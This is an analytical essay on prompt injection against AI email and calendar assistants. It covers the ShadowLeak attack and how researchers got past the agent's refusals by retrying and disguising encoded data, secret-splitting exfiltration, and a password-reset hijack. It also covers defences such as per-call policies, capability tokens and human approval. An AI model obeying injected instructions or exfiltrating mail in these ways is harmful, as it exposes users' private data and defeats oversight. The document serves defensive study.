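The contract left Dana's mailbox as an email, and the meeting summary stayed in the calendar. In a third case, mailbox data left through a web browser. *ShadowLeak*, a report by Radware, the security company that discovered the flaw, describes an attack on ChatGPT's Deep Research. In this mode, an agent spends up to half an hour reading sources and then writes a report. Users can connect Deep Research to Gmail as well as the web.

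The attacker sends the victim an email that looks like routine office business. The email's HTML contains instructions for the agent, which tiny or white text can hide from a human reader. Later, the victim asks the agent, Deep Research, to search the day's emails for information about a new employee. The agent finds a genuine message from the personnel department with the employee's name and home address, and it also reads the attacker's email. It then opens a URL on the attacker's server that contains the encoded name and home address, which the attacker reads from the server's log. The victim sees no sign of the request.

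Radware's researchers needed several attempts to get this far. The agent refused plain requests to send personal data to an outside site, and it treated the attacker's web address as suspicious and searched for it online instead of opening it. The researchers asked the agent about its tools, learned which one opened web pages directly, and read the reasoning it displayed. Their next message named the tool and told the agent to keep trying if a request failed, which helped because OpenAI's restrictions didn't block the same request every time. The agent then sometimes opened the page but left out the personal data.

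The researchers overcame the last obstacle by presenting encoding as a security measure. The model converted the name and address into a string of meaningless characters before calling the browsing tool, so any check on the tool received only that string. Radware reports that this version worked in every repeated test, but doesn't say how many it ran.

Earlier attacks, such as EchoLeak, relied on a program on the user's computer loading an image from an attacker's address when it displayed the answer. That program can restrict which sites images come from, and a company can monitor traffic from its employees' computers. In ShadowLeak, the request came from OpenAI's servers, where the victim's company could neither see nor block it. Radware found no comparable restriction on the addresses the agent could open. It reported the flaw in June 2025, and OpenAI fixed it in early August and marked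 it resolved on 3 September.

A credential broker would have made no difference, because the request that carried the data needed no credential. Anthropic's lists of allowed hosts, for example, limit where a credential goes but not which hosts the agent can contact. A separate list could limit the hosts, but an agent that researches on the web has to open pages that nobody listed in advance, so a strict list would prevent much of its work.

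### Calls that are harmless alone

A manipulated planner can do harm by passing information from one allowed call to the next. Reading Dana's mail reveals nothing to anyone else, but if the planner then opens a web page whose address contains text from that mail, the site receives the text. A component that judges each call separately can approve both calls and miss the theft.

*A Framework for Formalizing LLM Agent Security* (Siu, He and colleagues, 2026) gives an example from programming. An agent copies a sensitive file into a code repository and later makes the repository readable and writable by everyone. Each action may serve the user's task, but together they expose the file. To catch this, a check would have to track how earlier actions had changed the system.

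An attacker can also split one harmful call into several that look innocent. *Silent Egress* (Lan, Kaul and colleagues, 2026) tested this with an agent that previews web links. Many assistants fetch a page's title and description as soon as a link appears in the conversation, so a page can influence the planner through text the user never sees. An assistant that previewed the links in Dana's mail would have the same weakness.

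The agent in the experiment ran on qwen2.5:7b, a small open model. The user always asked for a summary of a page, the model's context always contained a secret, and the page contained instructions to send the secret to the attacker. Lan and colleagues varied where the instructions appeared on the page and whether the agent reached the page directly or through redirects. The agent sent a request to the attacker's server in 423 of 480 runs (88.1%). It sent none in 120 runs with ordinary pages. In 95% of the successful attacks, the answer the user saw looked harmless, so a safety check of the answer alone would have missed them.

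In half of the 480 runs, the instructions told the agent to split the secret into four pieces and send each in a separate request. Splitting made the attack less reliable but its traffic much harder to recognize. The agent contacted the attacker's server in 238 of the 240 runs without splitting and 185 of the 240 with it, according to the per-configuration results. The first request visibly contained sensitive data in 96.7% of the runs without splitting and 26.3% of those with it.

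The figures on splitting have a flaw, though. Lan and colleagues give a rate of 15.8% for sensitive data appearing anywhere in the first three requests, which is lower than their rate for the first request alone. That is impossible, because the first three requests include the first. The general result is still plausible, because four characters from the middle of a key look like any other four characters.

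The experiment also favored the attacker because the secret was directly in the model's context, the developer's instructions were minimal, and the model was small. The 88.1% therefore shouldn't be taken as an estimate for a commercial assistant.

Lan and colleagues also tested defenses. Two thirds of the attacks still succeeded when the model was told never to follow instructions from web pages. A list of allowed domains stopped all the attacks. Such a list is a much weaker defense for mail, because it has to include Dana's mail provider, which will deliver a message to almost any address.

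### Keys in the inbox

An attacker with access to a mailbox can use magic links to get into other accounts, as the Composio attacker did after stealing mail tokens. Many services also email password reset links or short codes that complete a sign-in.

A stranger who can manipulate Dana's assistant can reset her password on another service without stealing a token. He enters her address on the sign-in page of, say, her accounting service and asks to reset the password. The service emails her a link. In a message of his own, he tells the assistant to find the newest email from that service and forward it to him, and he opens the link before it expires. The assistant needs only permission to read and send mail, which it has.

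Reset links often expire within hours and sign-in codes within minutes, so this attack works poorly against an assistant that runs once a day when Dana asks. An assistant that handles each message as it arrives gives the stranger a much better chance. A service that also requires a code from an app on Dana's phone would keep him out even if he had the link.

Radware's *ShadowLeak* (2025), a shorter advisory on the same flaw, lists credentials, health records and legal strategy among the data a company could lose through it.

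The comparison with OpenSSH fails here. A broker can protect Dana's mail token as the monitor protects the server's key, but the mail API's ordinary read call returns reset links and sign-in codes as message text, and the harness puts that text into the planner's context. Blocking the assistant's access to message bodies would prevent this, but then the assistant couldn't read the meeting requests. The harness could instead withhold messages that look like password resets, but it might miss some and hide a few ordinary messages.

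### Whose right and whose intention

Writers on agent security often call all of these cases confused deputy problems. Siu and colleagues use the term more narrowly, and their distinction helps to show which checks can work. In simplified notation, three of their definitions are:

```
confused deputy      (user, target) ∉ R   and   (agent, target) ∈ R
capability misuse    (agent, target) ∈ R   and   H(action) = 0
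indirect injection   source ∉ S            and   H(action) = 0
```

*R* is the set of permitted accesses, so (user, target) ∈ *R* means the user may access the target. *S* is the set of authenticated sources, such as a user who has logged in. "Source" is the origin of the instruction the agent followed. *H* is 1 if the action serves the user's objective, given what the agent has done so far, and 0 if it doesn't. Capability misuse also requires that the agent's work as a whole is still directed at the user's task.

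In a strict confused deputy attack, the user asks the agent for something that the agent is allowed to access but she is not. Siu and colleagues give the example of an employee who asks to see everyone's salary, and an agent that uses its own access to the personnel database to fetch the figures. Similarly, an employee could ask for the director's messages from a company assistant that has permission to read every mailbox. Checking the employee's own rights would stop this, and the mail API would do that check if the assistant used the employee's delegated token.

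The same check doesn't protect Dana's contract, because she is entitled to read it and send it to anyone. Under these definitions, the theft is both an indirect injection and capability misuse. It is an indirect injection because the instruction came from an unauthenticated stranger and the action didn't serve Dana's request. If the planner had attached the contract to Lee's message by mistake, with no stranger involved, that would be only capability misuse.

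Lan and colleagues keep the older name, "confused deputy", but make a similar distinction. They write that in the traditional problem it is unclear whom the deputy is serving, while for an agent it is unclear what the user intended. Mellafe Zuvic also uses the term for a program that misuses its authority because of an attacker's text. Hardy's compiler fits both uses, because the user who named the billing file had no right to write to it.

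Siu and colleagues' framework permits an action prompted by an outside source if it serves the user's objective. They reject the simplest rule against injection, which is to ignore every instruction from an unauthenticated source, because a user may want the agent to follow outside instructions, such as those in a recipe. An assistant that answers mail spends most of its time handling such instructions. If Lee writes that three o'clock would be better and asks to include a colleague, the assistant should probably move the meeting and invite the colleague.

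This makes nearly everything depend on *H*, and the formula for a secure action doesn't quite match the explanation around it. Siu and colleagues describe a recipe website that tells a shopping agent which of the user's stored payment methods to use. They count this as a violation, even though the purchase serves the user's objective, because only the user should choose the payment method. But their formula requires *H* to be 1 for every action and accepts any source when *H* is 1, so the condition on sources never excludes an action that the other conditions allow.

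The same problem could easily arise in Dana's mail. Suppose the stranger asks the assistant to copy the meeting's confirmation to a second address. Dana asked the assistant to send a confirmation, so *H* could reasonably be 1, but the stranger chose one of the recipients. Whether Dana would object depends on who is at that address and what else the message contains.

Also, nobody can compute *H* reliably. Siu and colleagues call it an oracle, a function that defines what a perfect check would return without explaining how to build one. Another language model can judge whether an action serves the user's request, but it may be inconsistent, and an attacker can try to mislead it too. Finding out which text caused a model to act is an unsolved research problem.

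### How often models comply

The practical risk depends partly on how often a planner follows a stranger's instructions. *LivePI* (Zhao, Bhaskar and Dobriban, 2026) measured this with OpenClaw running on a live virtual server. The agent had working test accounts for Gmail and several chat services, and a cryptocurrency wallet with a small balance. The email tests combined ten ways of presenting the malicious instructions with five goals, for 50 cases per model. One goal was to forward a summary of recent private messages to an outsider, which is close to what happens to Dana.

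Zhao and colleagues counted an attack as successful only if the injected text influenced the agent and the attacker's goal was achieved. They used a language model to judge the results and also checked for real effects, such as a sent email.

| Model | Success through Gmail (50 cases) | Success in all tests (169 cases) |
|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.3-Codex | 20% | 27.2% |
| Gemini 3.1 Pro | 12% | 29.6% |
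| Kimi K2.5 | 6% | 16.6% |
| GLM-5 | 6% | 27.8% |
| Claude Opus 4.6 | 2% | 10.7% |

The Gmail figures are imprecise, since a rate of 2% means one success in 50 cases. If the cases were a random sample, the 95% confidence interval would run from about 0.4% to 10.5% for Claude Opus 4.6 and from 11% to 33% for GPT-5.3-Codex. The gap between those two models is probably real, but the order of the three in between could easily change. All five models date from before the summer of 2026, so the table doesn't show how newer ones would do.

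Instructions in a group chat succeeded in every case with every model, including Claude Opus 4.6. Zhao and colleagues traced this partly to the harness, OpenClaw, which labeled messages from anyone in the group as coming from the user but labeled email as tool output. The models treated text with the user label as a command, even when the sender had no connection to the agent's owner.

A mail assistant could easily have the same fault. If Dana pastes a stranger's email into the chat window, the stranger's text arrives labeled as Dana's. If the assistant has its own mailbox, a careless developer might treat every incoming message as a user's request.

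How often a manipulated planner attempts an unauthorized action also depends on the model. Mellafe Zuvic summarizes tests of 27 models from a companion study, in which the injected text presented a dangerous action as a necessary step in the user's own task. Twelve cost-optimized models, which a company might choose for high-volume routine work, attempted an unauthorized action at a mean rate of 0.603, compared with 0.189 for 15 flagship models. These are rates of attempts, because the test environment kept the calls from having any real effect.

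He gives no confidence interval for the difference, and both groups included models with high rates. Among the cheaper models, gpt-4o-mini attempted the action every time, while the preview version of Gemini 3.1 Pro, a flagship, never did. One person wrote all the attacks and decided which models counted as cost-optimized. Even so, the gap is large enough that a developer who moves a mail assistant to a cheaper model should retest it for injection.

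The wording of the attack can matter as much as the model. In separate tests, Mellafe Zuvic compared a crude demand with the same demand presented as part of the user's task. The second version raised the rate from 0.027 to 0.459 for mistral-large and from 0.283 to 1.000 for glm-4.7. A company that tested its assistant only with crude demands could conclude that mistral-large was almost immune.

AI companies also publish results in system cards, the documents that accompany a new model. Zhao and colleagues note that Anthropic's card for Claude Fable 5 and Claude Mythos 5 reports results on Agent Red Teaming, a benchmark built from a public competition in which people submitted 1.8 million attacks. The card also covers adaptive attacks on agents that write code or use a browser or computer. In these attacks, the attacker changes the text in response to the model's behavior. Most of the benchmark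 is private to make it harder to train models on it, so outsiders can't check how closely its attacks resemble a message sent to someone's mailbox.

None of these rates can be put into one ranking, because the tests count different things:

| Test | What counts as success | How the attacks were chosen | Result |
|---|---|---|---|
| ShadowLeak | Personal data reaches the attacker's server | Refined against one product until they worked | 100% in repeated tests |
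| Silent Egress | Any request reaches the attacker's server | Simple and fixed | 88.1% with one small model |
| LivePI, Gmail | The attacker's goal is achieved | Ten fixed techniques for five goals | 2–20%, depending on the model |
| 27-model sweep | The model attempts an unauthorized action | Written to fit the user's task | Means of 0.603 and 0.189 |

The preview version of Gemini 3.1 Pro had a rate of zero in the 27-model sweep, but in LivePI Gemini 3.1 Pro had the highest overall rate of the five models. The difference could come from the attacks, the harness, the definition of success or the model version, and the published figures don't show which.

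A low success rate also protects Dana less than it seems to, because sending email costs almost nothing. If a stranger sent 50 different messages, each with an independent 2% chance of success, the probability that at least one would work would be 1 − 0.98⁵⁰, or about 64%. Real attempts aren't independent, since a model that resists one message will probably resist similar ones, and a spam filter might block the sender. But if the stranger can get the same assistant, he can revise his message against his own mailbox, much as Radware's researchers did with Deep Research, and send Dana only the version that works.

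## Can a rule or a person check each call before it is sent?

The message that carried the contract out of Dana's mailbox was well formed and had a valid token. To stop it, a component outside the planner has to check the recipient and the attachment and decide whether this message may be sent. Deciding on each call this way, based on its actual values, is called per-call authorization. The component can apply rules or ask Dana.

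### Offering a tool and authorizing a call

Most agent software decides only which tools to offer the planner, which is coarser than checking each call. Mellafe Zuvic calls this capability gating, using "capability" to mean a tool rather than a right in Hardy's sense. If the developer of Dana's assistant leaves out the tool for deleting mail, the planner can't use it. But once he includes the tool for sending mail, the planner fills in the recipients, and the software treats any well-formed address as authorized.

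In the audit of June 2026 that found no default check of a call's values in three frameworks, Mellafe Zuvic traced what each one does between the planner's proposal and the tool's execution:

- *LangChain and LangGraph* look up the tool by name, usually check that the arguments have the right types, and run it. Developers can attach functions that observe each step, but these don't act as a dependable veto. A component that asks a human first is available, but the developer has to add it.
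- *LlamaIndex* checks that the tool exists and passes it the planner's arguments. If the planner asks for a tool that doesn't exist, LlamaIndex tells the planner so and raises no security alert.
- *The Stripe Agent Toolkit* lets developers limit the permitted actions and the rights of the API key. Within those limits, it forwards the planner's amounts, customers and redirect addresses to Stripe.

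The audit covers public source code at fixed versions, so it doesn't show what Stripe's own servers might check. Mellafe Zuvic doesn't claim to have found a vulnerability. Developers may not realize that the frameworks leave this check to them.

### ScopeGate's checks

ScopeGate, the control that Mellafe Zuvic built to fill this gap, receives the tool's name, its arguments and some trusted context, and returns "allow" or "deny". No language model takes part. It applies these checks in order:

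1. *Scope.* The policy must list the tool. This excludes misspelled tool names and tools the planner has discovered for itself.
2. *Authorization.* If the policy restricts an argument, its value must be on a list of approved values.
3. *Money ceiling.* The amount of a payment or refund must be a finite number between zero and a set limit.
4. *Idempotency.* Some calls need an idempotency key, an identifier that lets a service recognize a repeated request and avoid carrying it out twice. The key must come from the trusted context.
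5. *Default deny.* ScopeGate allows only calls that pass every check, and treats any error as a refusal.

The money check shows how easily this kind of code can fail. An early version let through an amount of NaN ("not a number"), a value computers use for results such as zero divided by zero. Any greater-than comparison with NaN is false, so a program that refuses amounts greater than the ceiling will accept it. The current version accepts an amount only if it is within the allowed range.

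### A policy for Dana's mail

Mellafe Zuvic tested ScopeGate mainly on payments. An equivalent policy for Dana's assistant might look like this:

```
search_mail, read_message, list_events:
    allow

send_message:
    to, cc, bcc       every address is in Dana's contacts
    attachments       none
    count             at most 10 messages per run
    idempotency key   required

create_event:
    guests            every address is in Dana's contacts
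    count             at most 10 events per run
    idempotency key   required

any other tool, or any error:
    deny
```

The count replaces the money ceiling. ScopeGate examines one call at a time, so the harness would have to keep the count and supply it as trusted context. The recipient rule covers `cc` and `bcc` because the stranger could otherwise receive a blind copy of a message to Lee. Calendar events need the same rule because a calendar service can email an event's description to its guests.

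Suppose this week's requests come from Lee, from Ana, who is another client, from Sam, whom Dana has never met, and from the stranger. The planner might propose these calls:

| Proposed call | Would Dana want it? | Decision |
|---|---|---|
| Confirm Thursday at 2 pm with Lee | Yes | Allow |
| Offer Ana a different day | Yes | Allow |
| Offer Sam half an hour on Friday | Yes | Deny, because Sam isn't a contact |
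| Send `contract.pdf` to `files@outside.example` | No | Deny, because the recipient isn't a contact |
| Send Lee a message that mentions Ana's price | No | Allow |

The planner can still search for the contract, but the policy stops it from sending the contract to the stranger, without having to detect the injection. The policy would also stop the assistant from forwarding him a password reset link.

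Refusing Sam is a more everyday problem. The developer could widen the rule to include anyone who asked for a meeting this week, but the stranger also asked for one, so he could have the assistant send the contract to the address he wrote from. The attachment rule would block the file, but the planner could paste the contract's text into the message. A safer exception would let the assistant write to new people only through a fixed template in which the planner chooses just the time. Sam would get his appointment, and the stranger could learn little more than when Dana is free.

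No rule in this policy would catch a message disclosing Ana's price to Lee, because Lee is the correct recipient and the rules don't check the text.

The developer also has to decide where to put the check. A check in the harness can read the tool's arguments directly, but a script in the sandbox might bypass it by calling the mail API through the broker. A check in a broker that forwards every request would also cover the script, but if the mail API requires encoded messages, the broker would have to decode each one to find the recipients. Mellafe Zuvic describes both placements but tested ScopeGate only inside the application.

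### The tests of ScopeGate

ScopeGate refused all 48 calls in a fixed set of bypass attempts. Some disguised a forbidden value with invisible characters, look-alike letters or changes of case. Others supplied the wrong type of data, altered a tool's name or left out the idempotency key. These tests had exposed the NaN error.

In another test, the language model GLM-5.2 played the attacker for 40 rounds and received ScopeGate's reason after each refusal. It produced 29 unauthorized calls, and ScopeGate refused them all. Nine other attempts were malformed, and two were harmless calls that ScopeGate allowed.

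These are good results, but a short program that compares values with a list should do well on such tests. The payment tests had only one approved account. Email addresses are harder to check, since an address in Dana's contacts might belong to a mailing group with outside members, and comparing strings wouldn't reveal that.

ScopeGate also allowed all ten legitimate calls in a control test, five from each of two models. Ten calls are too few to establish a rate, because a system that wrongly refused a quarter of legitimate calls would still have about a 6% chance of allowing ten in a row. The calls also came from a simulated payment agent. Merchants seldom change the account that receives their money, while a mail assistant frequently handles mail from new correspondents. How often the policy frustrated Dana would depend mostly on how many requests came from people like Sam, which the test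 doesn't measure.

### Who may write the rules

Dana's contacts are a fairly safe source for the recipient list because she maintains them herself. Mellafe Zuvic requires this kind of source. He forbids using a language model's output for any part of the policy, even if the model only helped draft the rules beforehand, and he requires the lists to stay fixed during a conversation. If the stranger's paragraph can make a model put an address into a call, it might also make a model add that address to the approved list, and the check would then accept it.

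In *Progent*, Shi, He and colleagues (2025) have a model write the rules from the user's request. They argue that fixed rules can't suit an assistant with many different tasks. The assistant needs to send mail when the user says "email Alice an update", but not when the user asks for a summary of unread messages. A policy that covers both tasks is too loose for the summary, and nobody can write a separate policy by hand for every possible request.

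Progent therefore creates a policy for each task:

1. Before the agent reads any outside material, a model reads the user's request and the list of tools, and writes rules about tools and their arguments. Progent refuses any call that no rule allows.
2. After each call, a model decides whether the rules might need changing. It sees the request and the call but not the result, which could contain hostile text.
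3. If a change might be necessary, a model reads the result and proposes new rules.
4. An SMT solver, a program that determines whether a set of logical conditions can all be true, checks whether the new rules allow any call that the old ones didn't.
5. If they don't, Progent applies them automatically. If they do, the change needs approval.

If *A(P)* is the set of calls that policy *P* allows, and *P′* is the proposed policy, the last two steps come down to this:

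```
A(P′) ⊆ A(P)    narrowing: apply automatically
A(P′) ⊈ A(P)    expansion: ask for approval
```

This answers much of Mellafe Zuvic's objection. The stranger's text may cause the model to propose a looser rule, but the rule takes effect only if a person or an automatic setting approves it.

Shi and colleagues tested Progent on AgentDojo, a benchmark that hides malicious instructions in simulated banking, travel, Slack and office tasks, including mail and calendar work. With Progent, the attack success rate fell from 39.9% to 1.0%, and the agent completed its tasks about as often. On a second benchmark, Agent Security Bench, the attack success rate fell from 70.3% to 3.9%.

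In these tests, the system approved every expansion automatically, to imitate a careless user, so the solver's check blocked nothing. The results show that a model can write good rules, but they don't test the guarantee meant to protect users when it writes bad ones. On AgentDojo, the initial rules alone reduced attack success to 2.5%. Human review of the initial rules and all expansions reduced it to zero, but Shi and colleagues assumed a reviewer who would reject any expansion that added a malicious address.

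Only 6% of the proposed updates on AgentDojo were expansions, which suggests that users would rarely have to approve anything. However, the setup also included fixed rules that allowed harmless read-only tools, which probably reduced the number of expansions. Dana's request is harder because it names no recipients. The model could initially allow mail to anyone, since anyone might have asked for a meeting, and the message with the contract would then pass without an expansion. Or the model could forbid all mail until the assistant had found the requests, and then propose to add Lee, Ana, Sam and perhaps `files@outside.example`. Dana would have to spot the wrong address. Shi and colleagues acknowledge that an ambiguous request or a mistaken approval can leave the agent with too much access.

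*Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) criticizes both ways of writing Progent's rules. People make mistakes when writing the rules by hand, and a model that updates the rules after reading hostile text may loosen them. The solver deals with the second problem only if whoever approves expansions is careful.

The two approaches can be combined. Mellafe Zuvic's argument is strong against rules that a model can loosen, but much weaker if the model can only tighten limits set by a person. Dana's developer could forbid attachments to anyone outside her contacts, and a model could add limits based on what she asked for, such as one message per meeting request. If the stranger manipulated that model, Dana might lose some legitimate replies, but the attachment rule would still apply.

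Progent supports fixed rules that take priority over the rules the model writes for the task. But it checks any call the fixed rules don't cover against the task's rules, so the developer has to write hard limits as explicit prohibitions. If the fixed rules only list permitted recipients, the model can still allow other addresses.

### AgentCap

*AGENTCAP* (Kabbinamakki Suresh and Gao, November 2026) returns to hand-written rules and combines them with Hardy's idea of a capability. The AgentCap system issues permissions for particular calls instead of giving the agent a tool for the whole session.

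The planner proposes a call and picks its purpose from a fixed list. A policy engine outside the planner checks the call and, if it passes, signs a token for one operation on one resource. The token is valid only for that agent and session, for a short time and a limited number of uses. A separate gateway checks the token just before the call runs. In the sample banking policy, a token for a transfer lasts 30 seconds and works once, and the agent must already have permission to read the balance.

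A manipulated planner can state a false purpose, so the other conditions provide most of the protection. AgentCap can forbid an agent to hold two dangerous permissions at once, such as access to sensitive data and a way to contact outsiders. It also checks whether a protected value, such as a recipient, came only from untrusted material.

Kabbinamakki Suresh and Gao tested AgentCap on AgentDojo and on InjecAgent, another injection benchmark:

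| Benchmark and model | Attack success, without → with AgentCap | User's task completed under attack, without → with AgentCap |
|---|---|---|
| AgentDojo, GPT-4o | 45.6% → 5.1% | 73.6% → 74.9% |
| AgentDojo, GPT-5.4 | 33.2% → 0% | 75.7% → 75.0% |
| InjecAgent, GPT-4o | 23.2% → 8.6% | 74.1% → 62.2% |
| InjecAgent, GPT-5.4 | 12.0% → 0% | 73.0% → 65.4% |

Each figure comes from a single run. Without an attack, AgentCap reduced task completion by between 3.1 and 11.7 percentage points. The attacks that still succeeded with GPT-4o aimed at the text of the agent's answer, used an argument that the policy didn't protect, or passed through a field that nobody had labeled as untrusted. The last two kinds of attack succeeded because of errors in the policy, which supports the complaint that people make mistakes when they write rules by hand. A tool that Kabbinamakki Suresh and Gao built to analyze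 policies also found a permission that no agent could obtain, because two rules conflicted.

They also ran Progent on AgentDojo. It completed 59.6% of the tasks under attack, compared with 74.9% for AgentCap. It often failed because its generated rules allowed only values the model had anticipated. This result contrasts with Shi and colleagues' finding that Progent preserved task completion, and it comes from a competing project. But the explanation is plausible, since a model that has read only Dana's sentence can't anticipate Sam's address.

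The comparison doesn't settle who should write the rules. Kabbinamakki Suresh and Gao froze their policies before running the tests, but they wrote them from the benchmark's tools and the descriptions of its user tasks, so they knew in advance what users would ask for. Shi and colleagues object to hand-written rules mainly because developers don't know this. Dana's developer could come close to knowing it by offering an assistant that only handles meeting requests. For a general assistant, he would need much looser rules or a way to derive rules from each request.

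### After a refusal

A planner may try something else when the software refuses a call. Progent's default refusal message suggests using other tools or arguments. This helps when the planner has made a mistake, but a planner influenced by the stranger may respond to a blocked email by putting the contract in a calendar invitation. *Let the Agent Do It?* (2026), a study of how software practitioners make permission decisions, notes that agents also look for other paths after a user refuses permission. This can feel like overreach if the user objected to the action and not just the method.

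The rules have to cover every way data can leave the mailbox and calendar, and repeated refusals should have consequences. AgentCap gives each agent a trust score, which starts at 0.8 by default and falls by 30% with each suspicious event. Three in a row lower the score to about 0.27, below the threshold of 0.3, so AgentCap revokes all the agent's permissions and isolates it.

This could work badly with a strict mail policy. If three people outside Dana's contacts asked for meetings on the same morning, her assistant could trigger the same response just by trying to answer them. Refusals for unknown recipients should probably count for less than attempts to attach confidential files.

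### A model as the approver

Some judgments are too vague to write as fixed rules and come up too often to ask the user each time. For these, Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* describes a second model that approves or blocks the calls of Claude Code, the company's coding agent. This approver sees the user's messages and the proposed calls, but not the tool results or the agent's explanations, so the stranger's paragraph would never reach it directly, and a manipulated planner couldn't give it reasons to approve a call.

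In Anthropic's tests, the approver blocked 0.4% of 10,000 ordinary calls. It missed 5.7% of 1,000 artificial attempts to steal data, and 17% of 52 real cases in which the agent had gone further than the user wanted. In most of the misses that Anthropic examined, the approver identified the danger but wrongly treated something the user had said as consent.

An approver like this would probably notice that a contract doesn't belong in a reply to a meeting request. But because it can't see Dana's mail, it can't tell whether Sam asked for a meeting or the planner took his address from a malicious message. Anthropic accepts this loss of information to gain resistance to injection.

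### Asking the user

The simplest form of human approval is a draft. The assistant writes and saves the replies, and Dana sends them from her own mail program, where she sees the exact recipient, text and any attachment that will go out. With Gmail, this still depends on a broker that blocks the assistant from sending.

Drafts for every reply would cost Dana much of the time the assistant was supposed to save. Hartman reduces the number of decisions by sorting requests for credentials into three tiers:

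| Requests | What happens |
|---|---|
| Low risk, authorized in advance and consistent with the agent's past behavior | The broker approves them automatically |
| Moderate risk, or outside the agent's usual behavior | A person receives a notification, and the broker refuses the request if there is no answer, by default after five minutes |
| High risk, destructive or administrative | The approver must also prove their identity with a security key or a similar method |

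For Dana's assistant, a plain reply to a contact could be automatic, a first message to Sam could require her approval, and an attachment to an outsider could require her security key. The five-minute limit is short for someone who spends the day in meetings. If it expires, the assistant should leave a draft so that Sam still gets an answer.

Hartman's human approver sees the agent's identity, the action, the scope and the agent's stated reason, which Hartman forbids his automated decision component to use. These details aren't enough for mail, because a request to "send mail to confirm a meeting" could hide the contract. Dana should see the actual message, with every recipient and attachment.

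The approval should then apply only to that message. The harness can store the proposed call, display the stored version, and send exactly that version once Dana approves it. If the planner changes an address or a sentence afterwards, it needs a new approval. Attackers can also target the approval process, for example by impersonating the approver.

Hartman lists several measures against approval fatigue, the tendency to stop reading requests after approving many of them. The broker can limit how many requests an agent makes, flag unusual patterns, and require a pause after several approvals. It can also present harmless requests as suspicious to test whether the approver is paying attention. He concedes that these measures reduce the risk but can't remove it.

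### How carefully people read approval requests

Most of the published data on approval fatigue comes from coding agents. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports that users approve 97% of permission prompts. The company's earlier post reported 93%. A high rate doesn't prove that users are careless, because most of the commands were probably harmless.

The same announcement reports a more informative experiment. Anthropic had a research vendor recruit 1,053 paid testers for a coding study without telling them what it was measuring. During each session, the vendor replaced one permission prompt with a clearly dangerous command. Only 143 testers (13.6%) refused it. Testers caught about 17% of the dangerous commands early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more prompts. Anthropic's automated approver blocked 89% of the same commands.

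Anthropic published these figures to justify making the automated approver its default. The testers also worked in a prepared environment with nothing of their own at risk, so Dana might be more careful with her own mail. But the stakes were equally low throughout the session, so repetition seems a more likely reason that the testers caught fewer commands as it went on.

Knowing about the danger may not make people check actions more carefully either. Wu, Wermke and colleagues (*From Delegation to Action Approval*, 2026) surveyed 203 developers who use coding agents. Of those who carefully reviewed most or all of the agent's code, 61% often approved at least one type of action without looking closely. Developers who knew of security or privacy incidents or concerning practices did this more often than those who didn't. The survey can't show why, and the sample wasn't representative. Perhaps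 the people who use agents most hear about more incidents and also see more approval prompts.

Participants in *Let the Agent Do It?* described clicking through familiar prompts and sometimes skipping review when short of time. A system that stops asking once a user has approved the same kind of call many times may therefore be treating approvals given out of habit as evidence of trust.

Poor approval prompts make this worse. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) examined 290 reports about agents and users' files. In 80 of them, the user had let actions run without approval, and 31 involved prompts that told the user too little. For example, a prompt may show the command `python3 setup.py` but not what the script will do to the user's files.

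Dana has some advantages over these developers. An email is easier to understand than a shell command, and she might review ten replies a week instead of hundreds of commands a day. None of these studies tested email, so they don't show how many malicious messages someone in her position would catch.

### One list for the whole task

People may also respond differently to a plan than to a series of permission requests. Anthropic reports that Claude Code users reject 39% of the plans it presents, compared with 3% of individual permission requests. Part of the gap must come from users who reject a plan because they want a better one, not because they noticed a danger. Still, the gap suggests that users read plans before answering.

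Dana's assistant could finish reading the requests and then show her everything it proposes to send:

| To | Message | Attachment |
|---|---|---|
| Lee | Thursday at 2 pm works for Dana. | None |
| Ana | Could we meet next Tuesday instead? | None |
| Sam | Dana is free on Friday at 3 pm. | None |
| `files@outside.example` | The document is attached. | `contract.pdf` |

Dana would be unlikely to miss the last line. She could remove it and approve the rest, and the harness would then send those three messages and refuse any others. This also solves the problem of Sam's address, because Dana authorizes it herself without first adding him to her contacts. Mellafe Zuvic's rule would exclude such a list because a model proposed its entries, but no entry takes effect until Dana approves it.

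This method suits an assistant that works through a batch of requests. An assistant that answers each message as it arrives has no complete list to show, so it would have to reply automatically to contacts and save drafts for everyone else. With either method, Dana has to read the text as well as the names. If the reply to Lee mentioned Ana's price, the recipient would be correct and there would be no attachment, so she could spot the mistake only by reading the text.

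## Can the part that reads mail be kept apart from the part that acts?

The policy for Dana's mail blocks a bad call after the planner has read the stranger's paragraph and followed its instructions. A developer could instead keep the paragraph away from any model that can send mail. OpenSSH did something similar by moving the code that handles strangers' input into an unprivileged process.

### One model reads and another acts

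*The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants* (Willison, 2023) proposes using two language models instead of one. The privileged model takes the user's request and has the tools for sending mail and changing the calendar. The quarantined model reads the messages and has no tools, because Willison assumes that an attacker may take control of it at any moment. *Agent Privilege Separation in OpenClaw* (Cheng and Tsao, 2026) divides the work in the same way between two agents, called the "actor" and the "reader".

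A message that controls the reader can also determine what the reader writes. Willison's central rule is therefore that the actor must never see the reader's text. A controller, which is ordinary software like the harness, stores the text and gives the actor only the name of a variable. If Dana asks for a summary of her latest email, the steps are:

1. The actor proposes to fetch the latest email and store it as `$VAR1`.
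2. The controller fetches and stores the message, and returns only the name `$VAR1`.
3. The actor asks for a summary of `$VAR1`.
4. The controller puts the message into a prompt for the reader and stores the reader's summary as `$VAR2`.
5. The actor proposes to show `$VAR2` to Dana, and the controller displays it.

The variable lets the actor refer to the stranger's text without seeing it, just as a broker's placeholder lets an agent refer to a token without seeing it.

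If the message contains the stranger's paragraph, the reader may follow its instructions, but it can't search for the contract or send it. The paragraph can still change the summary Dana sees. Willison warns that such a summary could persuade her to copy private data into a website, or could include a link or image that leaks the data through its address. The controller therefore has to restrict links and images.

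Willison allows one exception to his rule, for answers the reader chooses from a fixed set of categories, because the controller can check that an answer is in the set before passing it on. He calls his proposal "pretty bad" because it makes assistants harder to build and less pleasant to use, and because a single mistake that lets message text reach the actor undoes the protection. He later added that CaMeL, a Google DeepMind system, addresses a flaw in the proposal.

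### The LLMail-Inject contest

Cheng and Tsao tested a version of this separation against attacks from LLMail-Inject, a public contest to hijack a simulated email assistant. Abdelnabi, Fay and colleagues organized the contest and described it in *LLMail-Inject* (2025), though Cheng and Tsao credit it to Greshake and colleagues. Between December 2024 and April 2025, 839 participants made 461,640 submissions.

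Each submission was an email. The simulated user asked the assistant to summarize recent mail or answer a question about it, and the attacker had to make the assistant send a specified message to a specified address. The contest had four levels:

- *Level 1.* The assistant read two emails, one of them the attacker's.
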